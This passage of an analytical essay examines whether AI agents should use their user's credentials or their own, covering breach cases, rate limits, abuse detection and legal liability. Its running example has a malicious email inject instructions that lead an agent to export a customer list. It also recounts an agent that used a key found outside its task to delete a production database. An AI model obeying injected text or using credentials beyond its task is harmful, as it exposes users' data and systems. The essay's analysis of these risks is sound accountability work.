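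Vercel (2026) reports that the attacker used the app's access to take over the employee's Google Workspace account, and from there the employee's Vercel account. The attacker then moved into Vercel's internal systems and read customers' environment variables, which often contain keys and database passwords. Vercel encrypts all environment variables, but the attacker could decrypt the ones customers had not marked as sensitive.

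By this point, revoking the AI app's grant would not have been enough, because the attacker also had the employee's accounts. Vercel had to secure those as well.

Vercel hasn't published the total number of customers affected. It first reported a "limited subset" of customers and later found a small number of additional accounts. The theft at Context.ai may have affected hundreds of the app's users across many organisations.

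Customers had to replace the exposed API keys, tokens, database passwords and signing keys. Vercel warned them that deleting a project or their whole account wouldn't be enough, because the stolen keys could still give access to other systems. Context.ai's consumer product was already unavailable, but Vercel said on 19 April that its own services remained operational. Vercel declared the incident closed on 16 October.

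Vercel also published the AI app's client identifier and urged Google Workspace administrators to look for it. Administrators could use that one identifier to find the app in their employees' accounts and revoke its access. If employees had given the app their passwords instead, administrators would have had no identifier to search for.

### Whose allowance the agent uses

Whether a service can rate-limit an agent without affecting the user depends on which requests it counts together. Under GitHub's *Rate limits for the REST API*, a logged-in user can normally make 5,000 API requests an hour. GitHub counts all requests made with the user's personal access tokens and all requests that apps make on the user's behalf toward this limit.

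An organisation can also install an app that acts as itself rather than as a user, using a GitHub installation token. The app then gets its own allowance, which starts at 5,000 requests an hour and can rise to 12,500 for a large organisation, or 15,000 on the enterprise plan.

Suppose Maya's CRM copied these rules. crm-assistant makes 90 requests a minute, while her spreadsheet macro and other tools make 10.

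| | The agent uses Maya's key | The agent uses an installation token |
|---|---|---|
| Allowance | 5,000 an hour, shared | 5,000 an hour for each |
| When the agent runs out | After 50 minutes | After about 56 minutes |
| When Maya's tools run out | After 50 minutes | Never; they use 600 an hour |

If Maya's macro and the agent share a request allowance, the macro stops working for the last ten minutes of every hour, although it made only a tenth of the requests. If they have separate allowances, the agent still has to wait, but the macro keeps working.

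Naming the agent in the token wouldn't give it a separate rate limit under GitHub's rules. One kind of GitHub token identifies both an app and the user it acts for, much as a composite token does, but requests made with it still count toward the user's limit. To get its own limit, the agent has to act as itself, and then GitHub no longer restricts it to what Maya may do.

The rules can even favour the agent over the person. An app owned by an organisation on the enterprise plan may make 15,000 requests an hour for a user. In GitHub's example, such an app makes 10,000 requests, which puts the user's personal access tokens over their limit of 5,000 but leaves the app 5,000 more, so Maya's macro would stop while her agent carried on.

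If crm-assistant uses a copy of Maya's cookie, the CRM must slow both of them down or neither. Giving the agent its own key is enough in principle to limit it separately, as it is to revoke it separately, because the CRM could count requests for each key even when every key identifies Maya. GitHub instead counts requests from all of a user's keys together, presumably because people could otherwise raise their limit by creating more keys.

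Maya's company can also slow the agent before its requests reach the service. GitHub includes the number of remaining requests in each response. The program that runs crm-assistant could read that number and pause when 1,000 requests remain, leaving those for Maya. This works under impersonation and requires no change by the service. It fails if an attacker steals the key and uses it from another program.

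A shared request count can also lead people to blame the wrong party. PHP Boy Scout's *I blamed the agents for my rate limit* (2026) describes a developer running more than twenty agent sessions on one GitLab account, all using the developer's personal token. When GitLab began refusing requests in October, the developer assumed the agents were responsible and started giving them service accounts.

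The next morning the refusals continued, even though the agents had been idle all night. One of the sessions checked GitLab's count every ten seconds and saw it jump from 9 to 78 between two checks. A second jump, from 94 to 130, triggered a refusal message with a stated limit of 100. Both jumps happened while the developer was opening several proposed code changes in quick succession. Each page made an estimated 25 to 35 requests to load.

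This is one person's experience, and the number of requests per page is a guess. But it shows that a person can use up a shared allowance just by clicking, and that no one can tell from the total who used it. Automated build programs used their own tokens, so they didn't add to the developer's count. The developer still planned to keep the service accounts, mainly to make it clear which session had done what.

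### Abuse detection built around human speed

Besides enforcing fixed limits, services look for behaviour that suggests a stolen account or a spam program. They may check how fast requests arrive, how many run at once and the time of day. An agent working as its user intended can look suspicious on all three.

Under GitHub's additional rate limits, most requests that change something count as five points, and an account may use up to 900 points a minute on one part of the interface. That allows 180 changes a minute, or three a second. A person editing records by hand would never reach that rate, but an agent running several jobs in parallel could.

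GitHub also generally allows no more than 80 new items, such as comments, per minute and 500 per hour, including those made on its website. If Maya's CRM had the same limits and the agent added 500 notes under her name within an hour, she might be unable to add one herself. GitHub warns that it may apply such limits for undisclosed reasons and may ban an integration that keeps sending requests after a refusal.

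Two forum posts suggest that agents do trigger these systems, though neither proves it:

- In *Running tasks in the cursor cloud can result in GitHub being banned*, a user of the coding tool Cursor reports that GitHub blocked four of their accounts after they ran cloud agents. The reply, apparently from Cursor's staff, considers GitHub's abuse detection the most likely cause. The user had also kept creating new accounts, which could look suspicious without any agent.
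- In *Suspended from Antigravity & Gemini Code Assist*, a user suspended from Google's coding tools suspects that a system mistook their parallel chat sessions for a bot. They say they used only the official program. Google's reason for the suspension is unknown.

It can be hard to find out which check blocked or limited a request. GitHub's *When protections outlive their purpose* describes limits and blocks at several layers of its systems, and engineers may add more during an attack.

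If crm-assistant impersonates Maya, strict checks may lock her account when the 02:00 inbox job runs, leaving her unable to work in the morning. Looser checks would also let a thief who has stolen her cookie work quickly at night without setting off an alarm. If the agent has its own credential, the CRM's owners can keep strict checks on Maya's sessions and set different ones for the agent. The thief can't use the agent's looser limits without also stealing the agent's credential.

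A service can also be strict about where the agent logs in from, if the agent runs on a known set of servers. After the Drift theft, Salesloft published the network addresses that Drift used and told customers to treat a successful login from anywhere else as suspect. The same rule wouldn't work for Maya, who may log in from home, a hotel or a customer's office, or for an agent on her laptop, which travels with her.

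### Many agents for one person

Separate allowances solve Maya's problem but create one for the service. If she had twenty agents and the CRM allowed each of them 5,000 requests an hour, together they could make 100,000, twenty times the allowance of a colleague who does the same work by hand. Someone who wanted to copy the whole customer database could also divide the work among agents so that none of them stood out.

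Services have reason to worry about the volume. Tom's Hardware reports in *GitHub says massive influx of AI-generated code required extra 4 million CPU* that the number of saved code changes on GitHub grew sixfold in a year, to 7.4 billion a month. GitHub needed four million extra processor cores to handle the growth.

A service can avoid both problems by applying several limits to each request. For Maya, the CRM might set:

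```
each agent acting for Maya:          1,000 requests an hour
all agents acting for Maya:          4,000 requests an hour
Maya and her agents together:        5,000 requests an hour
```

One runaway agent would stop at 1,000, and the other agents could continue. All twenty together would stop at 4,000, leaving at least 1,000 for Maya's own tools. Adding a twenty-first agent wouldn't raise that combined limit.

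To apply these limits, the CRM must identify the agent making each request and the person it is acting for. A composite token identifies both. Separate keys under Maya's name could also work if she labelled each one as an agent's key and never shared it between programs. Separate agent accounts would make it easy to limit each agent, but the CRM couldn't add up Maya's total unless it also recorded whom each agent was working for.

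## Who answers for harm done with a user's authority

Blocking crm-assistant prevents another export but doesn't undo the one at 02:00. Maya's company must pay for an investigation and may face claims from customers whose details a stranger now has. A common objection to impersonation is that it puts the blame for such losses on the wrong person. South makes a version of this objection, warning that agents acting indistinguishably from their users create "accountability gaps".

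The argument is that Maya takes the blame for something that the agent, its maker or an attacker did, because her managers, and perhaps a court, rely on a CRM log that names her.

### How far the log decides who is blamed

If the agent's token identifies only Maya, only her name appears in the log, but the log is rarely the only evidence. Ines used the agent's own record to trace the export to the email. If the vendor had deleted that record, Maya would have had much less to show in her defence.

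A manager could suspend Maya that morning because of a single log line, but a court would hear other evidence. Every US state except New York has adopted the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act, drafted in 1999, according to Proskauer's *Contract Law in the Age of Agentic AI*. Under section 9, an electronic record is attributable to a person "if it was the act of the person", and either side can prove this in any manner. Evidence that a login procedure reliably identifies people counts, but the Act's official commentary says that using such a procedure creates no legal presumption. Maya could rebut the log line with the agent's record and the attacker's email.

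Maya could still be to blame even if the log correctly named the agent, so the last step doesn't follow. The same commentary treats an electronic agent as a tool, and a person's acts include what their tools do. It explains that the rule keeps a record from being ascribed to a machine instead of "the person operating or programing the machine". Proof that crm-assistant sent the request therefore doesn't settle who answers for the harm, because Maya started the agent, her employer deployed it and the vendor programmed it.

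The argument is therefore convincing about suspicion and discipline at work, where people act quickly on whatever record they have, but much weaker about legal liability.

### Whose act a program's act is

The Act defines an electronic agent as a program used to initiate an action or respond to records without a person's review. Section 14, as enacted in Massachusetts (Massachusetts Legislature, *Section 14*), allows two such programs to form a contract even if no individual knew what the programs were doing. If the email had told crm-assistant to accept an offer of $40,000 worth of office chairs, Maya's company couldn't escape the contract merely by showing that nobody had read it.

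The drafters were thinking of programs that follow preset rules, such as one that reorders stock when it runs low. In their commentary, they also anticipated software that could learn and devise its own instructions, and left courts to interpret the definition accordingly. The federal E-SIGN Act also accepts contracts made by electronic agents if the agent's action is "legally attributable to the person to be bound". TinyFish's *The Load-Bearing Word*, a company publication, points out that the statute never defines what makes an action attributable.

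Courts would probably turn to the common law on representatives, which distinguishes actual authority from apparent authority. Actual authority covers what a representative reasonably understands they may do, given what the person they represent has told them. Apparent authority exists when something the represented person said or did leads an outsider to reasonably believe that the representative may act. If a company tells a purchasing clerk to spend no more than $1,000 but has honoured her larger orders for years, a supplier who doesn't know about the limit can usually hold the company to her next larger order.

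Maya asked crm-assistant to update customer records. No sensible assistant would read that as permission to send the whole customer list to a stranger, so the agent had no actual authority for the export. But the token it presented to the CRM allowed exports. A broad token can therefore make an agent appear to have authority that the user never meant to give.

Whether the token names the agent could matter here. Apparent authority assumes that the outsider knows it is dealing with a representative. If the CRM receives only Maya's name, its operator has no reason to think that it is, and a court might instead ask whether Maya and her employer protected her credential properly. If the CRM receives a composite token, which also names the agent, the court could ask what the operator had reason to believe about that agent. If Maya's company had told the operator that agents may not export customers,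 the operator could hardly claim to have believed that this one was allowed to.

All of this applies the law of representatives by analogy, because software isn't a legal person. PYMNTS's *AI Agents Can Move Money, But They Can’t Pay for Their Mistakes* (2026) reports that existing US law can't hold an agent itself responsible. *Legal Framework for AI Agent Liability Remains Undefined*, a summary of an analysis by the law firm Venable, says the traditional doctrine doesn't clearly cover AI agents that exceed their intended scope.

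### Handing over the means of payment

Payment law is more definite, since people have long lent each other cards and PINs. Regulation E governs electronic transfers from US consumer accounts. Its *§ 1005.2 Definitions*, published by the Consumer Financial Protection Bureau, defines a transfer as unauthorised if someone other than the consumer initiates it without actual authority and the consumer gets no benefit. Banks bear most of the loss from unauthorised transfers that customers report promptly.

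The definition excludes transfers by anyone to whom the consumer gave a means of access, such as a card or code. If a customer gives a relative or co-worker her PIN and that person takes more than agreed, she is fully liable until she tells the bank that the person's transfers are no longer authorised.

Suppose Maya gives a household-budget agent her bank login to pay bills, and it sends $2,000 to the wrong company. The regulation's definition of "person" includes organisations but not software, so the agent can't be the person who made the transfer. If the agent is her tool, Maya made the transfer herself. If the agent's vendor made it, she gave the vendor the means of access by supplying her login. She probably bears the loss either way, unless the vendor has to compensate her.

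The law firm Goodwin's *Authorizing Agentic Payments* (2026) also concludes that the law presumes such a transfer to be authorised, even if the agent exceeded what the customer intended. *New Reg E Liability* (2026), by the law firm Dickinson Bradshaw, is less certain. It warns that banks might unknowingly take on the risk of agents' mistakes, and notes that banks can be liable for incorrect transfers as well as unauthorised ones.

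*AI Agent Liability*, a blog post (Inteligencia, 2026), reports that three US banks (Citi, PNC and Citizens) now say they hold a customer responsible when an AI agent misuses the customer's account. A bank can't use its terms to remove rights that the statute gives consumers, so these statements help the banks only if they have read the regulation correctly.

The rules differ for other kinds of payment. Goodwin's analysis supports this comparison:

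| Payment | What the rule looks at | If the agent exceeds the user's wishes |
|---|---|---|
| Transfer from a consumer account (Regulation E) | Whether the consumer furnished the means of access | The consumer usually bears the loss |
| Consumer credit card (Regulation Z) | Whether whoever initiated the payment had actual, implied or apparent authority | The charge arguably counts as authorised, but the consumer can dispute goods that she didn't accept or that didn't arrive as agreed; the merchant then usually bears the loss |
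| Business payment or wire transfer (Article 4A of the Uniform Commercial Code) | Whether the bank followed an agreed, commercially reasonable security procedure in good faith | The customer is generally bound, even if nobody authorised the payment |

The rule for business payments comes closest to what critics of impersonation fear, because a correctly used credential can be enough to bind the customer to a payment. But the customer is bound because it agreed to the procedure, and adding the agent's name to the bank's log wouldn't undo that agreement. Naming the agent wouldn't change the result under Regulation E either, where Maya pays because she handed over her login.

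An agent's name in the bank's log could still help in two situations, one of which is prompt injection. Regulation E treats a transfer as unauthorised if the person who made it obtained the means of access from the consumer through fraud or robbery. If a malicious email tricked the budget agent into revealing Maya's login and a thief used it, she would have a reasonable claim. If the email instead made the agent send the money itself, the thief would never have had the login, so she would have to argue that the thief had initiated the transfer. The name would help show which of these happened.

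The other is a withdrawal of permission. Once Maya tells the bank that the agent is no longer authorised, the bank can have to bear the loss from the agent's later transfers. If the bank can identify the agent, it could then refuse the agent's requests without replacing Maya's login.

### Disputes between the user and the agent's provider

Goodwin thinks it is fairly clear how losses are divided between customers and banks, but expects disputes between users and the companies that provide their agents to be harder to resolve. Courts would have to decide these disputes case by case, based on what the user said, how the agent interpreted it and what records exist.

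In the firm's example, an agent books a flight that meets every condition the traveller set, but allows only one hour to clear customs, recheck bags and catch a connection. The traveller can argue that the ticket had to be usable, even though the instructions didn't say so. The provider can answer that the agent followed the instructions it received. Both sides would agree that the agent made the booking, so a token identifying the agent wouldn't settle the dispute.

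Payment networks have begun to require better evidence. According to Goodwin, Visa requires providers to register, verify the user's instructions, enforce limits that match what the user delegated and keep detailed records. Chargeflow, a company that handles payment disputes, says Visa's new duties for agent platforms begin on 24 October 2026 and include no separate dispute rules for agents. A provider that complies can avoid fines from the network, but its users can still bring claims against it.

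The European Union may regulate these purchases more directly. Article 26 of the Digital Fairness Act, which the European Commission proposed on 11 November 2026, covers consumer contracts concluded by AI agents. According to Chargeflow, the article would require control settings for consumers and disclosure of conflicts of interest. EU Internet Law & Policy Blog's *The Digital Fairness Act* (2026) reports that the Commission could fine companies up to 6% of worldwide turnover for some breaches, and that the rules would apply 12 months after entering into force. Parliament and the member states' governments have yet to take positions.

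Users may also try to cancel a mistaken purchase under section 10 of the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act. Stanford Law School's *From Fine Print to Machine Code* (2025) describes the section as letting customers reverse a transaction if the agent gave them no way to prevent or correct an error. The section's wording is narrower, covering an error that an individual makes in dealing with another person's electronic agent, such as typing 1,000 instead of 100 into a shop's automated order system. An error by the customer's own agent fits that wording poorly.

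### Who could bear the loss from Maya's export

When a customer list is stolen, who must compensate the customers depends mostly on contracts, negligence and data protection law, which vary from place to place. Payment rules don't cover the theft, and the contract rules above don't settle who owes compensation. The person who wrote the email is the most to blame, but Maya's company will probably never find them. Four other parties could bear part of the loss.

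**Maya** started the agent and gave it a broad task, but she didn't ask for the export and was asleep when it happened. The customers dealt with her company and would gain little by suing a salaried employee. Her main risk is losing her job, and a log with only her name in it increases that risk.

**Her employer** would probably pay first. The customers entrusted their details to the company, and the common law generally makes employers liable for wrongs that staff commit in the course of their work. In Europe, the main duty to protect personal data falls on the organisation that decides why and how to use it. The company also let the agent have export rights it didn't need. A composite token doesn't identify who created the agent or who authorised its access. Jai Dargan, who heads the identity company Hydden, told Stojan that this is the first question after an incident.

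**The agent's vendor** made a product that followed instructions in a stranger's email. Maya's employer could claim that the vendor broke its contract, was negligent or sold a defective product. The vendor would probably reply that its terms put the risk on customers and that prompt injection is well known. Stanford Law School asks whether such disclaimers are enough, and whether it would be good policy to treat customers as accepting the risk just by using an agent. One reason for doubt is that the vendor can change how the agent treats text in emails, while Maya can't.

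**The CRM's maker** received a valid token that included the right to export. If the token named only Maya, the maker seems to have done nothing wrong, unless its contract promised to catch unusual exports. If the token named the agent and the maker's software failed to enforce a rule against exports by agents, Maya's employer would have a much stronger claim against the maker.

Contract terms may matter more than any of this evidence. Suppose the theft costs Maya's company $400,000 and the vendor's contract limits its liability to a year's fees, $30,000. Even with perfect proof against the vendor, the company could recover at most $30,000 from it, unless a court refused to enforce the limit.

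Changing one fact at a time shows what moves the blame:

| Changed fact | Whose position gets worse | What the agent's name would add |
|---|---|---|
| The company had banned AI agents, and Maya pasted her own key into one | Maya | Nothing, because her key doesn't carry the agent's name |
| An administrator had approved the export right without checking whether the agent needed it | Her employer | Proof that the agent used the right |
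| The vendor had promised that the agent ignores instructions in emails | The vendor | Proof that the agent made the request, though not why |
| The CRM's maker had agreed to block exports by agents and didn't | The CRM's maker | The information it needed to apply the block |

If only the token changes, responsibility shifts much less. The employer still has to answer to its customers, and the vendor's product still has the same flaw. Maya can more easily show that she didn't click "Export" herself. Only the CRM's maker may face a new argument, because it received information it could have acted on. The name provides evidence and can make it possible to carry out a contractual duty, but it doesn't create that duty.

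### The Kiro outage at Amazon

A 13-hour disruption at Amazon Web Services in December 2025 shows how people can agree that an agent was involved and still disagree about blame. The Financial Times reported in February 2026 (*Tech giant blames ‘user error, not AI error’ for incident in December*) that engineers had let Kiro, Amazon's own coding agent, change a system that customers use to examine their cloud costs. Four people familiar with the matter said the agent chose to "delete and recreate the environment".

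Amazon replied in a public statement that the cause was user error, "specifically misconfigured access controls", and not AI. It said the event affected one service in one of its 39 regions and led to no customer inquiries. In its view, any developer tool or manual action could have caused the same problem.

Both accounts suggest that Kiro used the engineer's permissions rather than a separate set of its own. Employees told the newspaper that Amazon treated its AI tools as an extension of the operator and gave them the same permissions. Amazon said the engineer had "broader permissions than expected". Neither account includes which credential Kiro presented or what the receiving system logged, so the public evidence doesn't establish whether Kiro impersonated the engineer in the sense of RFC 8693.

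The employees considered it foreseeable that an agent with an operator's permissions and no supervision would cause an outage. Amazon said that someone had configured access wrongly and that the AI tool's involvement was a coincidence. Both accounts can be partly true, because excessive permissions made the deletion possible and the agent chose to delete. Amazon also sells Kiro, so it has a commercial reason to blame the settings.

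The accounts conflict more directly about a second incident. Employees described an earlier outage involving another Amazon coding tool. Amazon first told the newspaper that "both instances" were user error and that the earlier one hadn't affected a customer-facing AWS service. It later called the claim that a second event affected AWS "entirely false".

Engineers normally need a second person's approval for such changes, but the newspaper's sources said they didn't need it in these cases. Amazon afterwards made peer review mandatory for access to production systems, the ones customers use. In March, after a series of outages in its retail business, it moved to have senior engineers approve AI-assisted changes, Ars Technica reported in *After outages, Amazon to make senior engineers sign off on AI-assisted changes* (2026). Both measures make a second person answerable for a change, whatever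 name the agent acts under.

### Whether naming the agent lets people disown it

Some critics worry about the opposite error, in which a log that names crm-assistant helps people avoid blame. Maya can say that the agent did it, and her company can say that a vendor's product acted outside its instructions. *Who is the 'I' in AI?* (Ramil, Al Kafi et al., 2026) calls this "liability evasion" and lists it among the threats that an identity system for agents should address.

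Brinsa (2026), in *Rogue AI Is Becoming a Corporate Alibi*, objects to how companies describe such incidents. One of his examples is PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses. In April 2026 a coding agent there ran into a credential problem, found a cloud-hosting key in a file unrelated to its task, and used the key to delete the company's production database. "The agent went rogue" describes part of this but omits who left the key within the agent's reach and who gave the key the power to delete the database.

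Officials and courts have shown little sympathy for this defence. Brinsa reports that Andrew Ferguson, chairman of the US Federal Trade Commission, refuses to treat AI agents as independent actors. In *Moffatt v. Air Canada* (2024), a Canadian tribunal held the airline liable for wrong information from its website chatbot, although the airline had suggested that the chatbot was a separate legal entity responsible for its own actions. In June 2026 a German court held Google liable for its AI search summaries. *AI and Liability* (Schneier, 2026) reports that the court treated the summaries as an expression of Google's business and rejected the defence that users can check the answers for themselves.

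In both rulings, a company's own system gave people false information. Neither involved an agent using someone else's credential, and the Ninth Circuit left claims for such harm open in Amazon's case against Perplexity. The rulings suggest that a company can't avoid responsibility by blaming its software, but they don't divide a loss among a user, an employer and a vendor.

Defenders of composite tokens reply that these tokens keep the user's name, so Maya couldn't deny that the agent was using her authority. The worry applies more to a separate agent account, whose log records only the agent's name. A company that uses such an account needs a record of who owns it and who gave the agent each task.

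Ramil and colleagues want to tie an agent's acts more strongly to a responsible person, using a cryptographic grant that expires. The grant would make it hard for that person to deny having authorised the agent, but it wouldn't show that they had authorised a particular act or that it would be fair for them to pay.

The second name also doesn't stop a company from shifting blame onto its staff. Maya's employer could point to her name in the log and not mention the administrator who approved the export right. The company's register of agents could identify that administrator if it recorded who approved each permission, when and for what purpose. Ines could then look up "crm-assistant" and find who had let it export customer records.
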